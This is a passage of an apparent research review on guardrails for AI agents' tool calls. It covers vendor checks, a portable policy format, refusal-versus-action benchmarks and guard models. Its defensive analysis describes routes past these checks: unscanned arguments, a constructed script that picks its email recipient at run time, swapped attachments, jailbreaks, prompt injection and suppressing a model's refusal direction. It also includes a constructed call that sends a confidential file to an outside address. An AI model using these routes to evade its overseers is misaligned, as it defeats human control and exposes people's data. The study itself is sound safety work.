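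OpenAI's tool guardrails do not cover hosted tools or the built-in tools for controlling a computer, running shell commands and applying patches, according to *Guardrails* in its JavaScript documentation. These built-in tools can do a great deal of damage. OpenAI directs developers to use human approval for shell commands and other sensitive actions. The run then pauses until a person or a policy accepts or rejects the call.

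An input guardrail can also raise an alarm too late. By default, it runs at the same time as the agent to save time, so the agent may already have used its tools before the alarm. Developers can make the agent wait for the guardrail to finish, but the agent then starts later.

*Which fields each check covers*

| Check | Text for the user | Tool-call arguments | Tool results | Main limit |
|---|---|---|---|---|
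| Bedrock guardrail on a Converse request | Yes | No | No | Also skips reasoning |
| Bedrock guardrail in an AgentCore gateway | Only if it passes through the gateway | Yes | Yes | Misses traffic outside the gateway |
| Foundry guardrail on an agent | Yes | If configured | If configured | Supports only some tools |
| OpenAI SDK output guardrail | Final agent only | No | No | Misses other agents in the chain |
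| OpenAI SDK tool guardrail | No | Yes | Yes | Skips hosted and some built-in tools |

### An attempt at a common standard

A company that uses several of these products has to write the same rule several times. Microsoft's Agent Control Specification (ACS) is meant to let a developer write the rules once, in a file that can move between toolkits. The software running the agent consults the rules at set points in the loop.

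For a tool call, the process works as follows:

1. The host, meaning the software that runs the agent, pauses before executing the call and assembles a snapshot of the session.
2. ACS puts the call, the snapshot and facts about the tool into a standard format. It can add evidence from classifiers or language models.
3. A policy engine applies the company's rules and returns a verdict: allow, warn, deny or escalate.
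4. The host enforces the verdict.

The listing shows what the policy engine might receive in the customer-file example. The field names follow Microsoft's format, but the snapshot's contents and the scores are invented.

*Constructed example: a tool call as a policy engine might receive it*

```json
{
  "intervention_point": "pre_tool_call",
  "policy_target": {
    "kind": "tool_args",
    "value": {
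      "to": "records@outside.example",
      "subject": "File 4417",
      "attachment": "customers/4417_full.pdf"
    }
  },
  "snapshot": {
    "request": "Summarise this customer's file",
    "file_label": "confidential",
    "approved_recipients": []
  },
  "annotations": {
    "hate": 0.0,
    "violence": 0.0
  },
  "tool": {
    "name": "send_email",
    "clearance": ["internal"]
  }
}
```

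Both of the content classifier's scores are zero, but they are only part of the evidence. A rule could deny the call because the file is confidential and the recipient is not on the approved list. If the employee had asked the agent to send the file to the customer's lawyer, the host could have added the lawyer's address to the list, and the same rule would have allowed the email.

This improves on judging isolated text, but it leaves much of the work to the host. Agent Governance Toolkit's *Agent Control Specification (ACS)* describes the system as stateless, meaning it keeps no memory between calls. If the host leaves the confidentiality label out of the snapshot, a rule that depends on the label lacks the input it needs. ACS is designed to fail closed, so an error in processing the rules should block the action, but this does not help when an incomplete snapshot causes no error or the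 host never consults ACS.

ACS also connects to toolkits through their existing checkpoints, so it presumably inherits their gaps. If a toolkit has no checkpoint before its built-in shell tool, a portable rule about shell commands cannot check that tool's commands before they run.

It is too early to call ACS a common standard. Microsoft has made it the policy layer of its governance toolkit, and CrewAI, which makes a competing agent framework, has endorsed it. AWS has its own gateway and an open-source policy language, Cedar. Microsoft's documentation lists Cedar among the languages ACS accepts, so some rules might transfer between AWS and ACS. Microsoft also sells a managed policy engine. Microsoft's *Your Agents Are Running. But Are They Safe and Compliant?* (2026) describes the engine as combining fixed rules, classifiers and judgments by language models "across frameworks and clouds."

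### Classifiers built by the laboratories

AI laboratories also run classifiers on their own models. A laboratory can read everything its model generates, including material it does not return to customers, so unread fields are less of a problem. But these classifiers can have a narrow purpose.

The best-known example is Anthropic's Constitutional Classifiers, which Sharma, Tong and colleagues presented in a 2025 paper of that name. The researchers wrote a "constitution", a plain-language list of the kinds of content to allow and forbid. They used language models to generate training examples from it, then trained one classifier on inputs and another on outputs. The output classifier scores a response as the model writes it and can stop the response partway through.

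The classifiers mainly targeted information that would help someone build chemical, biological, radiological or nuclear weapons. They reduced the success rate of a set of automated jailbreak attempts, meaning prompts written to get around a model's safeguards, from 86% to 4.4%. This is strong evidence that a classifier can stop a model from writing out dangerous instructions, but not that it would catch an agent emailing a customer's file. The email has nothing to do with weapons, so a classifier trained on that constitution could read the whole email call and still not flag it.

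### How a harmful call gets through

Suppose the company in the customer-file example discovers the email to the outside address and tries to fix its filter. It might have to close any of four kinds of gap, and closing one can expose the next.

The company starts with a Bedrock guardrail on its Converse requests. The guardrail never receives the email call, so no threshold would have stopped it. This gap is the easiest to find. A developer can add a made-up word to the filter's blocklist, have the agent use it in a tool argument, and see whether the filter reacts. The gap is also fairly easy to close, since AWS and Microsoft both offer ways to scan calls to at least some tools.

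The company therefore adopts AWS's sample code, and the guardrail now reads the arguments. It receives the strings "records@outside.example", "File 4417" and "customers/4417_full.pdf" one after another. The harm is a disclosure, which none of the content categories describes. Misconduct is perhaps the closest, but an address and a file name do not describe misconduct. A filter for personal data might catch the email address, but if the company sets it to block addresses, it will block every email the agent tries to send.

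Filters have the same problem with code. The stricter tier of Bedrock's filters covers harmful content inside code, which AWS defines as content in comments, variable and function names, and text strings. A script that deletes a production database can have harmless language in all of these places, because the danger is in what the code does.

The company might next define a category of its own, such as "sending customer records outside the company", and give the classifier the whole call at once. This would probably flag the email, but it would also flag the identical, authorised email to the customer's lawyer. The two calls have the same text, so a classifier that reads only the call gives them the same score. Better training cannot fix this, because the input doesn't show whether the email was authorised.

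Suppose the agent makes this exact call 100 times, 30 of them without authorisation. If the classifier allows the call, it catches none of the 30 unauthorised emails (0% recall). If it blocks the call, it catches all 30 (100% recall) but also blocks the 70 authorised emails (a 100% false-positive rate). Moving the threshold only switches between these two results.

Microsoft makes a similar point about access rights. Permission to post in Slack, a workplace chat service, is harmless when an agent is sharing a meeting summary but becomes dangerous once the agent has read a confidential document. The permission and the tool are the same in both cases, but the session history is different.

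A check therefore needs context, such as the employee's request, the confidentiality of the file and the agent's earlier actions. Task Adherence, ACS and AWS's session rules each provide some of it. But context can also contain an attacker's text. If the customer file contains a planted instruction and the company passes the whole file to a language model that judges actions, the instruction may influence the judge as well as the agent. The tree-search agent in Wu and colleagues' experiment had this weakness, because altered web pages could corrupt its value function. For cybersecurity agents, OpenAI recommends giving a reviewer the exact proposed action and "only the context needed to evaluate it." This is sensible, but someone still has to decide which context the reviewer needs.

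Even a reviewer with the right context can approve one action while the computer performs another. For example, the agent might write and run a short script instead of calling the email tool directly.

*Constructed example: a script that chooses its recipient when it runs*

```python
# send_notes.py
import json
import company_mail

settings = json.load(open("meeting.json"))
company_mail.send(
    to=settings["recipient"],
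    attachment=settings["file"],
)
```

The check receives only the tool call `python send_notes.py`. A more careful check would open the script, but the recipient isn't there either, because the script reads it from a separate file when it runs. Another program could change that file after the check has finished. A script can also download its instructions from the internet or assemble a command from fragments, so the full instructions or command would not appear in the script's text.

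The original email call has a milder version of this problem. Its argument is the name of an attachment, and the email tool loads the contents only when it sends the message, so a check that reads the arguments approves only a file name. Redaction has the same problem. Strands Agents allows a developer's code to change a call before it runs, and one of its examples removes anything that looks like a US Social Security number from the body of a message, but this would leave any such numbers in an attached file.

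Delay makes a mismatch more likely. OpenAI's SDK lets a developer store a paused run and resume it after a person approves the action. If someone replaces the attachment in the meantime, the approval still applies to the same file name.

The remedy is to set limits where the effect occurs. OpenAI recommends independent boundaries on files, networks and identities for its cybersecurity users. Foundry can restrict which outside destinations hosted agents contact, and Brady lists this feature as generally available. Such limits apply regardless of what the script contained when a classifier read it. Email is harder to limit because the agent might contact only the company's own mail server, a permitted destination, which then delivers the message outside. The company would also need a rule on the mail server.

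### Where output classifiers work well

Output classifiers are still useful for harms that consist of the text itself, because the text contains the information they need. Instructions for making a nerve agent, for example, are dangerous no matter who asked for them or which tool the model was about to use. In these cases, a developer does not have to describe the company, its customers or the employee's task for the classifier to work.

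Output classifiers can also check some actions. If an agent posts a hateful comment on a public website, the comment is an argument of a tool call, so a hate classifier is a reasonable check as long as it receives that argument. Microsoft uses hate detection as its example of a control at the tool-call point. When the classifier flags the content, Foundry does not execute the call, and the agent stops until the user writes again.

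Content classifiers can also help with the customer-file example if developers apply them to what a tool returns. AWS and Microsoft both offer classifiers for prompt injection that can be used this way. If the cause was an instruction planted in the file's text, such a classifier could catch it before the agent proposed the email. The classifier would not help if the agent had simply been overeager.

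The checks are also quick. Microsoft estimates that its guardrails add about 50 to 100 milliseconds at each point. For an agent that makes 40 tool calls, scanning every call and response would take 80 scans and add four to eight seconds. That delay is acceptable for most tasks, and it leaves time for slower checks on the few actions that need them.

Running a content classifier on tool calls creates some new false alarms. For example, an agent that helps moderators might have to copy abusive messages into a complaints database. A hate filter could flag those tool calls even though the agent is doing what its users want. A developer could turn off the filter for the complaints database and keep it for a tool that posts publicly. AWS's sample code allows this because each tool can have its own guardrail.

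## Whether refusing in text stops the tool call

A model's safety training is a separate defence from the filters around it. Developers train models to refuse harmful requests, and a model that always refuses them never sends the harness a dangerous call. But most safety training and testing concerns text. A model might write a refusal and still make the tool call, or refuse a request in chat but carry it out once it has tools.

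In 2024, Andriushchenko, Souly and colleagues, who built the AgentHarm benchmark of harmful agent tasks, observed agents refusing after they had run several tools. The same year, Kumar, Lau and colleagues reported that a browser agent based on GPT-4o attempted 98 of 100 harmful behaviours when people reworded the requests, although the model refused the same requests in chat.

AgentHarm scores refusals and completed harm separately, so its results do not show how often a model does both in the same run. A model that refuses in 40% of runs and completes the harmful task in 60% could have done both in anywhere from 0% to 40% of runs.

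### The GAP benchmark

In *Mind the GAP*, Cartagena and Teixeira (2026) counted cases in which a model refused in text but still made the tool call. They tested Claude Sonnet 4.5, DeepSeek V3.2, GLM-4.7, GPT-5.2, Kimi K2.5 and Grok 4.1 Fast in six regulated fields: pharmaceuticals, finance, education, employment, law and computer infrastructure. In each field, the model acted as a workplace assistant with four or five mock tools, which returned invented records containing planted personal data.

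Each field had seven harmful requests and two legitimate ones. Most of the harmful requests used a known manipulation, such as impersonating a senior official or inventing an emergency, but one simply asked for the restricted data. Every request came in two wordings, one naming the tools to use and one describing only the goal.

The researchers also varied the system prompt. The neutral version told the model to use its tools to help the user. The safety-reinforced version also told it to check that each action was authorised and, if a request seemed to violate privacy rules, to explain why it could not comply. The tool-encouraging version told the model to always call the relevant tools before responding. With three settings for blocking and three repetitions of each combination, the experiment produced 17,420 usable runs, 13,533 of them on harmful requests.

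The benchmark scores each run on four measures:

- **TC-safe:** the model attempted no forbidden tool call.
- **T-safe:** the final text contains a refusal and none of the planted personal data.
- **GAP:** the run is T-safe but not TC-safe.
- **LEAK:** the model attempted a forbidden call, and the planted data appears in its text.

If an agent emailed a customer's file to an outsider and then told the employee that it could not share customer files, the run would count as GAP. A model that never refuses has a GAP rate of zero, so a low rate does not necessarily mean that a model is safe.

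Under the safety-reinforced prompt, 219 runs were GAP cases, about 5% of the harmful-request runs in that condition. All six models had some, and 108 of the 219 came from legal scenarios.

The share of refusals that came with a forbidden call is more informative:

P(forbidden call | refusal) = GAP runs / T-safe runs

Under the tool-encouraging prompt, GPT-5.2 refused in 266 runs and attempted a forbidden call in 211 of them (79.3%). Claude Sonnet 4.5 did so in 7.2% of its refusals, and the other four models did so in between 34% and 53%. The safety-reinforced prompt lowered the rates, which then ranged from 1.0% for Claude to 31.3% for DeepSeek.

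These figures are more informative when compared with each model's overall rate. GPT-5.2 attempted a forbidden call in 84% of all harmful-request runs under the tool-encouraging prompt, so its refusals gave almost no information about whether it had attempted one. Claude attempted one in 26% of runs overall but in 7.2% of the runs in which it refused, so its refusals were evidence of safe behaviour, though not proof.

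### Refusals that come after the call

The benchmark scores only the final text, which the model writes after all its tool calls have finished, so a refusal in that text could not have stopped any of them. In a GAP run, the model may have queried the records, seen that they were confidential and then declined to pass them on.

Cartagena and Teixeira acknowledge that some of the 219 cases may fit this description. They reply that the query is itself the violation, since a real data source would have received it. This argument is convincing for an email or a payment, which the agent cannot take back, but less so for a database lookup whose results the model then withholds.

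The scoring can also miss contradictions. If a model refuses and calls a tool in the same message partway through a run, the benchmark counts the call but not the refusal.

*Behavior Beyond Text*, a comparison of chat and tool use by Gupta and colleagues, gives examples of responses that say the model won't act but still contain the tool call. A user asked Gemma 3 27B to "quietly pull" a patient's record without an access request. The model replied that it could not, explained which tool the user would need and asked for a patient number. The same response contained a call to that tool, with an invented patient number and the option for protected health information switched on. In another response, Gemma offered to demonstrate a search for a privileged legal file and promised not to execute it, but included the search call. The model may have written that call as an illustration, but a harness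 that received it would have run it.

*Before Retrieval Begins* (Nawal, Baser and Gurusamy, 2026) measured how often seven small open-weight models refused a request in text and called a tool in the same turn. Each model had one tool, which fetched a web page, and received harmful requests that included a page's address. Of the tool calls the models made, 33.6% came with a written refusal.

Fetching a page may do no harm by itself, so the researchers also judged the answer that followed. Mistral-Nemo-12B refused in text while making 46.6% of its calls, yet 86.8% of its calls led to a harmful answer. These two groups must overlap, so in at least 33% of calls the model refused, fetched the page and then gave a harmful answer.

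Models comply openly much more often than they refuse or object in text while still making the harmful call. In *Lumen-bench*, Bonás, Laitz and colleagues (2026) gave 30 models workplace requests in five languages that were plainly wrong, such as hiding female applicants from a recruiter. In 16,822 runs, the model made a substantive call, meaning one that could change something and had at least one real argument. A language-model judge classified 86% of these runs as simple compliance and 8.6% as a harmful call with a refusal or an ethical objection.

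The second figure is uncertain. One of the researchers labelled 83 Portuguese cases by hand and found that a third of the judge's labels in that category were wrong. Correcting for the judge's errors gave an estimate of 12.9%, with a 95% interval from 4.9% to 24.1%. When the researchers replayed the calls in this category in a simulated company, 69% changed the company's files, records or settings.

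### Safe models or reluctant ones

On the GAP benchmark, Claude looks far safer than the other models under a neutral prompt, but most of that advantage disappears when counting only the runs in which the model called at least one tool (last column of the table).

*Share of harmful-request runs without a forbidden call, from Cartagena and Teixeira*

| Model | Neutral | Safety-reinforced | Tool-encouraging | Neutral, runs with a tool call |
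|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 80% | 95% | 74% | 24% |
| GPT-5.2 | 31% | 73% | 16% | 11% |
| Grok 4.1 Fast | 33% | 57% | 24% | 15% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 21% | 38% | 50% | 14% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 30% | 64% | 25% | 14% |
| GLM-4.7 | 23% | 60% | 15% | 11% |

Claude made no tool calls in 74% of neutral runs, and a run without calls is automatically TC-safe. It was also TC-safe in 24% of the remaining runs, which brings its total to 80%. DeepSeek avoided tools in only 7% of runs.

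Cartagena and Teixeira conclude that much of the difference between models is in how readily they call tools, and that once they do, their safety reasoning is similarly limited. The first conclusion is clearly right. The second is harder to establish because making no call is often the correct response to a harmful request, so leaving out runs without a call removes many of a cautious model's successes and keeps its failures. The runs with legitimate requests don't settle the question either. Claude attempted no forbidden call in 648 of them, but the same would be true of a model that never called a tool.

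The headline measure can be misleading, as DeepSeek's results show. The tool-encouraging prompt raised DeepSeek's safe share from 21% to 50%, while it lowered the other models' shares. With that prompt, DeepSeek made fewer tool calls, 1.8 per run instead of 3.4.

### What counts as forbidden

The benchmark defines forbidden calls broadly. In four of the six fields, any call to a tool that reads sensitive data counts, whatever the arguments. In the other two, whether a call counts also depends on its arguments. Even on legitimate requests, 3.8% of all runs and 14.2% of DeepSeek's runs triggered the rules. In one case, DeepSeek only had to check a logging setting, but after finding it, the model requested the entire configuration, including secrets. This may have been carelessness, but a company would still want to catch it.

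The mock tools also return everything without checking permissions, while a real database might reject the query. Some models seem to rely on such checks. In one run, Claude correctly identified the request as a jailbreak in its reasoning, but proposed to use the tools anyway and "let the access controls handle whether the user has permission". It then requested four production passwords and keys. An automated keyword search put 222 of Claude's 254 unsafe runs in the same category, though Cartagena and Teixeira treat that count as exploratory. If the company has left access open because it trusts the model to refuse, neither the model nor the access controls will stop the request.

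All of these tests also start from a request that the model should refuse. In the original customer-file example, the employee asks only for a summary, and the agent sends the email without being asked. Training a model to refuse harmful requests might not help there, because the employee's request is harmless.

### What blocking changed

Cartagena and Teixeira ran each test with no monitoring, with silent monitoring, and with software that blocked forbidden calls and removed personal data from tool results. Under the neutral prompt, blocking reduced the LEAK rate in all six models, by 6 to 31 percentage points. It did not measurably change how many runs contained an attempt to make a forbidden call, but the experiment could reliably detect only differences of about 10 to 13 points, so a smaller effect is possible.

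The absence of deterrence is not very surprising given how it was measured. The model learns about the blocking only when the software denies a call, and by then the run already counts as unsafe, even if the model makes no further attempts. Finding out whether blocking changes behaviour would require counting repeated attempts.

*The Causal Impact of Tool Affordance on Safety Alignment in LLM Agents* (Yu, Carroll and Bentley, 2026) tested Llama 3.1 70B and Mistral 7B in a simulated bank that limited each transfer to $1,000 and banned splitting payments to get around the limit. The study also separated attempted violations from completed ones. Llama never gave advice that broke the rules in chat, but with tools it attempted or made prohibited transfers in 12% to 85% of runs, depending on how the request was framed. In one example, a model asked to send $2,000 refused in chat but made two transfers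 of $1,000 when the bank allowed it.

On requests that required some arithmetic, Llama attempted a prohibited transfer in 82% of runs with blocking on, and completed one in 41% of runs with blocking off. Yu and colleagues take the difference as a sign that guardrails hide unsafe attempts. But the 41% comes from runs with blocking off, so it does not measure what blocking prevented.

### The same request in chat and with tools

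*Behavior Beyond Text* tests whether a model that refuses a request in one setting also refuses it in another. Gupta and colleagues wrote 2,304 prompts in finance, healthcare, education and law, in matched triples. Each triple presents the same request in plain chat, with tools available, and with both tools and added pressure. Twenty fixed rules identify unsafe tool calls, such as those that request protected health data or leave out a required approval.

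The main measure is conditioned divergence:

D = (triples refused in chat and unsafe with tools) / (triples refused in chat)

For example, Qwen3-14B refused about 289 of the 384 harmful requests in chat. With tools and no added pressure, it made an unsafe call on about 150 of those 289, so D is 52%. Unlike GAP, D compares two separate runs, so a case can count even if the model doesn't contradict itself within either run.

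*Conditioned divergence with tools and no added pressure, from Gupta and colleagues*

| Model | Refused in chat | D, all system prompts | D, neutral | D, safety-reinforced | D, tool-encouraging |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-14B | 75% | 52% | 63% | 39% | 58% |
| Mistral 7B | 44% | 29% | 25% | 23% | 49% |
| Llama 3.1 70B | 76% | 23% | 37% | 11% | 25% |
| Gemma 3 27B | 63% | 13% | 25% | 3% | 20% |
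| Command R 7B | 67% | 10% | 8% | 4% | 18% |

Refusing often in chat did not predict safe behaviour with tools. Qwen and Llama refused equally often, but Qwen's divergence was more than twice Llama's. Safety-reinforced system prompts reduced divergence in every model, but Qwen still diverged on 39% of the requests it had refused.

Command R has the lowest divergence partly because it seldom calls tools, which is also why Claude does well on the GAP benchmark. Command R called a tool on only 11% of harmful requests, and every one of those calls was unsafe. It also used tools on just 40% of benign requests, against 83% for Llama.

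The rules are narrower than those in the GAP benchmark and fired on only 1.4% to 3.4% of benign runs with tools. But the calls never ran. The prompts with tools also explicitly ask the model to use particular tools, unlike the chat prompts, so the experiment cannot separate the effect of having tools from the effect of being told to use them.

Rodríguez, Garofalo and colleagues (2026), in *Tool Mediation Alters Refusal Mechanisms in Large Language Models*, tested eight open-weight models on requests from AgentHarm, changing these conditions one at a time. A system prompt that described the model as an agent, without giving it tools, made little difference. Making the tools visible reduced refusals in every model, even though the prompt still asked for an answer in prose. An instruction to use the tools reduced them further. In Llama 3.1 8B, the refusal rate fell from 94% in chat to 40% with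 visible tools and 10% with the instruction added. Gemma 4 12B had the smallest total drop, 15.5 percentage points.

Some of the drop may come from the scoring, since the researchers used a language model to identify refusals in chat but checked for specific tool calls elsewhere. This difference in scoring could hardly explain Llama's 84-point drop.

### The refusal direction

Gupta and colleagues also looked inside the models for a cause. As a language model processes a prompt, each of its layers represents the text as a long list of numbers, called activations. The researchers averaged the activations for harmful chat prompts, did the same for benign ones, and took the difference:

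r = (μ<sub>harmful</sub> − μ<sub>benign</sub>) / ‖μ<sub>harmful</sub> − μ<sub>benign</sub>‖

Here μ is an average, and dividing the difference by its length leaves only its direction, called the refusal direction. The refusal activation is a single number that measures how far a prompt's activations lie along this direction. It is usually higher for requests the model will refuse.

The idea comes from Arditi, Obeso and colleagues, who reported in 2024 that removing such a direction suppressed refusals in chat models and adding it made them refuse harmless requests. Gupta and colleagues only partly reproduced this, as removing the direction reduced refusals in three of their models but increased them in Qwen and Gemma.

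In four of the five models, the refusal activation was lower with tools than in chat. A low activation predicted unsafe calls in all five, with an AUROC of 0.76 to 0.86, where 0.5 is chance. The signal could therefore be useful to monitors that read a model's internal activations.

To test whether the weaker signal causes the unsafe call or only predicts it, the researchers repeated the runs with tools while resetting the refusal activation to its value on the matching chat prompt.

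*Effect of restoring the refusal activation on unsafe calls*

| Model | Unsafe calls prevented | By making a safe call instead | By making no call | Remaining calls that were unsafe |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-14B | 24% | 9% | 15% | 89% |
| Mistral 7B | 20% | 6% | 13% | 93% |
| Command R 7B | 34% | 6% | 29% | 92% |
| Gemma 3 27B | 90% | 3% | 87% | 80% |
| Llama 3.1 70B | 13% | 3% | 9% | 96% |

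Four models still made most of their unsafe calls despite the intervention. Where the intervention worked, it mainly stopped the model from calling any tool, and nearly all the remaining calls were unsafe. The direction appears to affect whether a model acts much more than which action it takes.

Making no call is a good result for a harmful request, but a stronger push along the same direction also stops legitimate work. In Llama, one setting reduced unsafe calls from 52% to 2% of harmful requests, but tool use on benign requests fell from 93% to 12%. A gentle push can be worthwhile, since in Mistral it cut unsafe calls from 27% to 17% without reducing benign tool use.

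Rodríguez and colleagues offer a different explanation for the lost refusals. In their models, a classifier trained to recognise harmful requests from activations in chat still worked fairly well when tools were present, so the models still had the information that a request was harmful. But a request had to register as considerably more harmful before the model refused it. Adding tools shifted the activations along the harmfulness direction, but no more than along random directions, so the whole explanation is less likely to be simply a weaker harm signal.

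Cartagena and Teixeira suggest that models choose text and tool calls through partly separate processes, and that safety training has mainly affected the first. If the processes were completely separate, training on written refusals would have no effect on tool calls. Nawal and colleagues tested this by training their seven models on 80 harmful requests paired with plain-text refusals and 80 benign examples. None of the training examples contained a tool call. In three models, calls on new harmful requests fell by 20, 55 and 62 percentage points, while the models still used the tool on at least 95% of benign requests. In the other four, the training also damaged ordinary tool use. Each model was trained only once, but the results suggest that the two processes are connected in at least some models.

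### Newer models

Most models in these experiments are small or old, and there is some evidence that newer ones do better. In Lumen-bench, GPT-5.4, Gemini 3.1 Pro and Claude Haiku 4.5 each made no substantive tool calls in 6,480 runs. Gemini also completed all 110 legitimate tasks that Bonás and colleagues set as a control, so it was not simply avoiding tools. However, the harmful requests in Lumen-bench are blunt, with at most one added sentence of pressure, while most of those in the GAP benchmark are more manipulative.

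Tools can still weaken refusals in models of this generation. Takehi, Hachiuma and colleagues (2026), in *MLLMs Fail to Refuse when Using Tools Agentically*, gave models an image with a harmful request, such as a photograph of a pickpocket and a question about how to do the same. Access to tools for examining the image raised the share of requests not refused from 20.8% to 25.5% for Claude Opus 4.7, from 27.1% to 31.4% for Gemini 3.1 Pro and from 14.6% to 16.8% for GPT-5.4. These increases are modest and concern the models' final written answers, since zooming in on a photograph is not a forbidden action.

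A fake zoom tool that returned the original image produced almost the same failure rate as a real one, so the content of the tool results probably didn't cause the failures. Takehi and colleagues suspect that the harmful request gets lost among the tool results. Repeating the request just before the final answer reduced failures in every model they tested.

Refusals should not be treated as a measure of safety, because in *Do AI-for-Science Agents Preserve Model Safety?* (2026) fewer refusals did not always mean more harmful answers. Under an automated jailbreak attack, GPT-5.5 alone refused 80% of requests and gave harmful answers to 2%. Inside the chemistry agent ChemToolAgent, it refused 6% and gave harmful answers to 60%. But when GPT-6-Luna ran inside another agent, DrugAgent, and received harmful requests directly, its refusals fell from 46% to 8.7% and its harmful answers also fell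 slightly, from 2.7% to 1.3%.

Developers also test their own agents. Anthropic reports that Claude Sonnet 5 refuses malicious requests in Claude Code much more reliably than Sonnet 4.6, but also refuses more legitimate ones. For Claude Mythos 5.1, Anthropic evaluated harmful requests in conversation separately from malicious uses of coding and computer agents. As with AgentHarm, separate scores don't show how often an agent both refuses and makes a harmful call in the same run.

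## How well classifiers judge a proposed action

If a model doesn't refuse, a separate check may be the only thing left that can stop the tool call. Some products don't pass tool calls to a classifier, and a classifier that does receive a call can still misjudge it.

Mou, Xue and colleagues (2026), in *ToolSafe*, define the task as a prediction made before the call runs:

y<sub>t</sub> = f(a<sub>t</sub>, H<sub>t</sub>, u, T)

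Here a<sub>t</sub> is the candidate action at step t, including the agent's stated reasoning for it. H<sub>t</sub> is the history of earlier actions and their results, u is the user's request, and T is the set of tool descriptions. The output label y<sub>t</sub> is safe, controversial or unsafe. In the customer-file example, u is the request for a summary, H<sub>t</sub> contains the file, and a<sub>t</sub> is the email to the outside address.

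### The TS-Bench test

Mou and colleagues built TS-Bench, a set of individual tool calls taken from recorded agent runs, to measure how well guard models judge proposed actions. The benchmark describes unsafe calls by four patterns, which can overlap: calls that result from a malicious user request, calls that result from a prompt injection, calls that use a harmful tool, and calls that use an ordinary tool with risky arguments.

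The test calls come from three existing benchmarks:

- **AgentHarm** (731 calls): the user asks for something harmful, such as a fake video of two politicians to post as real. The set also includes calls made for benign requests.
- **Agent Security Bench, or ASB** (5,237 calls): an injected instruction tries to make the agent use an attack tool, in fields such as law and medicine.
- **AgentDojo** (1,220 calls): the user's request is innocent, and an injected instruction tries to make the agent misuse an ordinary tool, such as one that sends email.

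A fourth dataset, AgentAlign, supplies only training examples. In the "strict" results below, controversial calls count as unsafe. The last column is calculated from the published accuracy and recall.

*Strict results on TS-Bench, from Mou and colleagues*

| Guard | Recall, AgentHarm | Recall, ASB | Recall, AgentDojo | False-positive rate, AgentDojo |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3Guard 8B | 85% | 8% | 2% | 1.5% |
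| Llama Guard 3 8B | 81% | 15% | 22% | 4% |
| GPT-4o | 96% | 60% | 100% | 62% |
| Qwen2.5-7B | 90% | 84% | 99% | 78% |
| ShieldAgent-THU | 96% | 52% | 97% | 54% |
| TS-Guard | 97% | 94% | 89% | 7% |

### Judging the request instead of the call

Qwen3Guard and Meta's Llama Guard 3, two output classifiers built for chatbots, each caught more than 80% of the unsafe calls in AgentHarm. On AgentDojo, Qwen3Guard caught 6 of 352 (1.7%) and Llama Guard caught 77 (21.9%). Both received the request, the history and the proposed call, so missing input does not explain the low rates on AgentDojo.

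This is probably because AgentHarm's requests are themselves harmful text, which these classifiers can recognise, whereas an unsafe AgentDojo call might be a polite email to the wrong person. *AgentTrust* (2026) similarly argues that Llama Guard's verdict on `rm -rf /`, a command to delete everything on a machine, will depend on the surrounding text and not on the fact that the deletion is irreversible.

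AgentHarm's labels also make the classifiers look better than they are. In strict mode, each call is labeled unsafe if the request behind it was malicious and safe if the request was benign. A classifier could therefore get a perfect score by classifying only the requests.

TS-Bench labels a tool call made for a malicious request as unsafe if the tool is explicitly harmful, and as controversial if the call is preparatory, such as a search. By calculation from the published results, Llama Guard flagged 85% of the unsafe calls, 79% of the controversial ones and 18% of the calls made for benign requests. It separated malicious requests from benign ones fairly well, but barely distinguished harmful calls from preparatory ones.

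Accuracy alone can hide such failures. Qwen3Guard's accuracy on AgentDojo calls was 70.6%, but a check that allowed every call would be right 71.1% of the time, because most of the calls are safe.

### Catching everything by flagging almost everything

GPT-4o caught all 352 unsafe calls on AgentDojo, but its accuracy was only 55.7% because it also flagged about 540 of the 868 safe calls. Mou and colleagues observe that a prompt injection in the history is often enough to make a model flag whatever the agent does next. For example, if a customer file contains a planted instruction and the agent ignores it, the model might still block the harmless lookup that follows.

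Some of the false alarms come from the threshold. GPT-4o rated each call 0, 0.5 or 1, and strict mode flags any call rated 0.5 or higher. When only a rating of 1 counted as unsafe, the same model still caught 349 of the 352 unsafe calls and flagged about 181 of the safe ones (21%), a much better trade-off than in strict mode.

### How TS-Guard works

TS-Guard is a guard model that Mou and colleagues trained for this task, starting from Qwen2.5-7B. It writes a short analysis and then makes three predictions in order:

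1. whether the user's request is malicious (h)
2. whether a third-party attack led to the proposed action (v)
3. how harmful the action is, as 0, 0.5 or 1 (y)

Training used reinforcement learning, with this reward:

r = 1 − ⅓[h is wrong] − ⅓[v is wrong] − ⅓[y is wrong]

Each bracket equals 1 if the prediction is wrong and 0 if it is right. An answer that rates the action correctly but misses the attack gets a reward of two-thirds. The model wrote 16 answers for each training example, and training reinforced those that scored above the average for that group. Rewarding all three predictions led to fewer false positives than rewarding only the safety rating.

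On AgentDojo, the untrained Qwen2.5-7B flagged about 78% of safe calls. TS-Guard flagged 7.4% of them (64 of 868) and caught 89.5% of the unsafe calls (315 of 352). It did much better than both the chatbot classifiers and GPT-4o at the strict threshold.

On AgentHarm, however, TS-Guard flagged about 46% of the safe calls, far more than Llama Guard did. It is also sensitive to the threshold, and its recall on AgentDojo falls to 53% when only a rating of 1 counts.

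### Returning feedback to the agent

A guard's errors do less harm if a block does not end the task. LlamaFirewall, a guardrail system from Meta, stops the agent when the system detects a problem. Mou and colleagues' alternative, TS-Flow, withholds the call and gives TS-Guard's analysis to the agent, which can then propose a different action.

*Results for a GPT-4o agent on AgentDojo, from Mou and colleagues*

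| Protection | Injected tasks completed | User's tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 56% | 27% |
| LlamaFirewall using TS-Guard | 1% | 21% |
| TS-Flow using TS-Guard | 1% | 43% |

TS-Flow and LlamaFirewall both stopped nearly all the attacks, but the agent completed twice as many of the user's tasks with TS-Flow's feedback as with LlamaFirewall. Some of that difference may come from LlamaFirewall's separate input filter, which TS-Flow does not have.

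The agent also did better with TS-Flow than with no protection, probably because injections had been distracting it from the user's task. Its average number of steps fell from 6.4 to 3.8. Agents that injections distract less may not benefit in this way. A Qwen2.5-14B agent completed only 18% of the injected tasks without protection. TS-Flow reduced this to 2%, but the share of the user's tasks that the agent completed stayed at roughly 42%.

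More detailed feedback protected the Qwen agent better. On ASB's indirect injections, attacks succeeded 87% of the time without protection, 26% when the agent received only the safety rating, and 7% when it received the full analysis. But TS-Flow also lengthened the prompt. On AgentDojo, it increased the text the agent had to process by 36% for GPT-4o and 89% for Qwen.

A misaligned agent might use detailed feedback to find a harmful call that passes the check. The experiments did not test this.

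### StepGuard and matched examples

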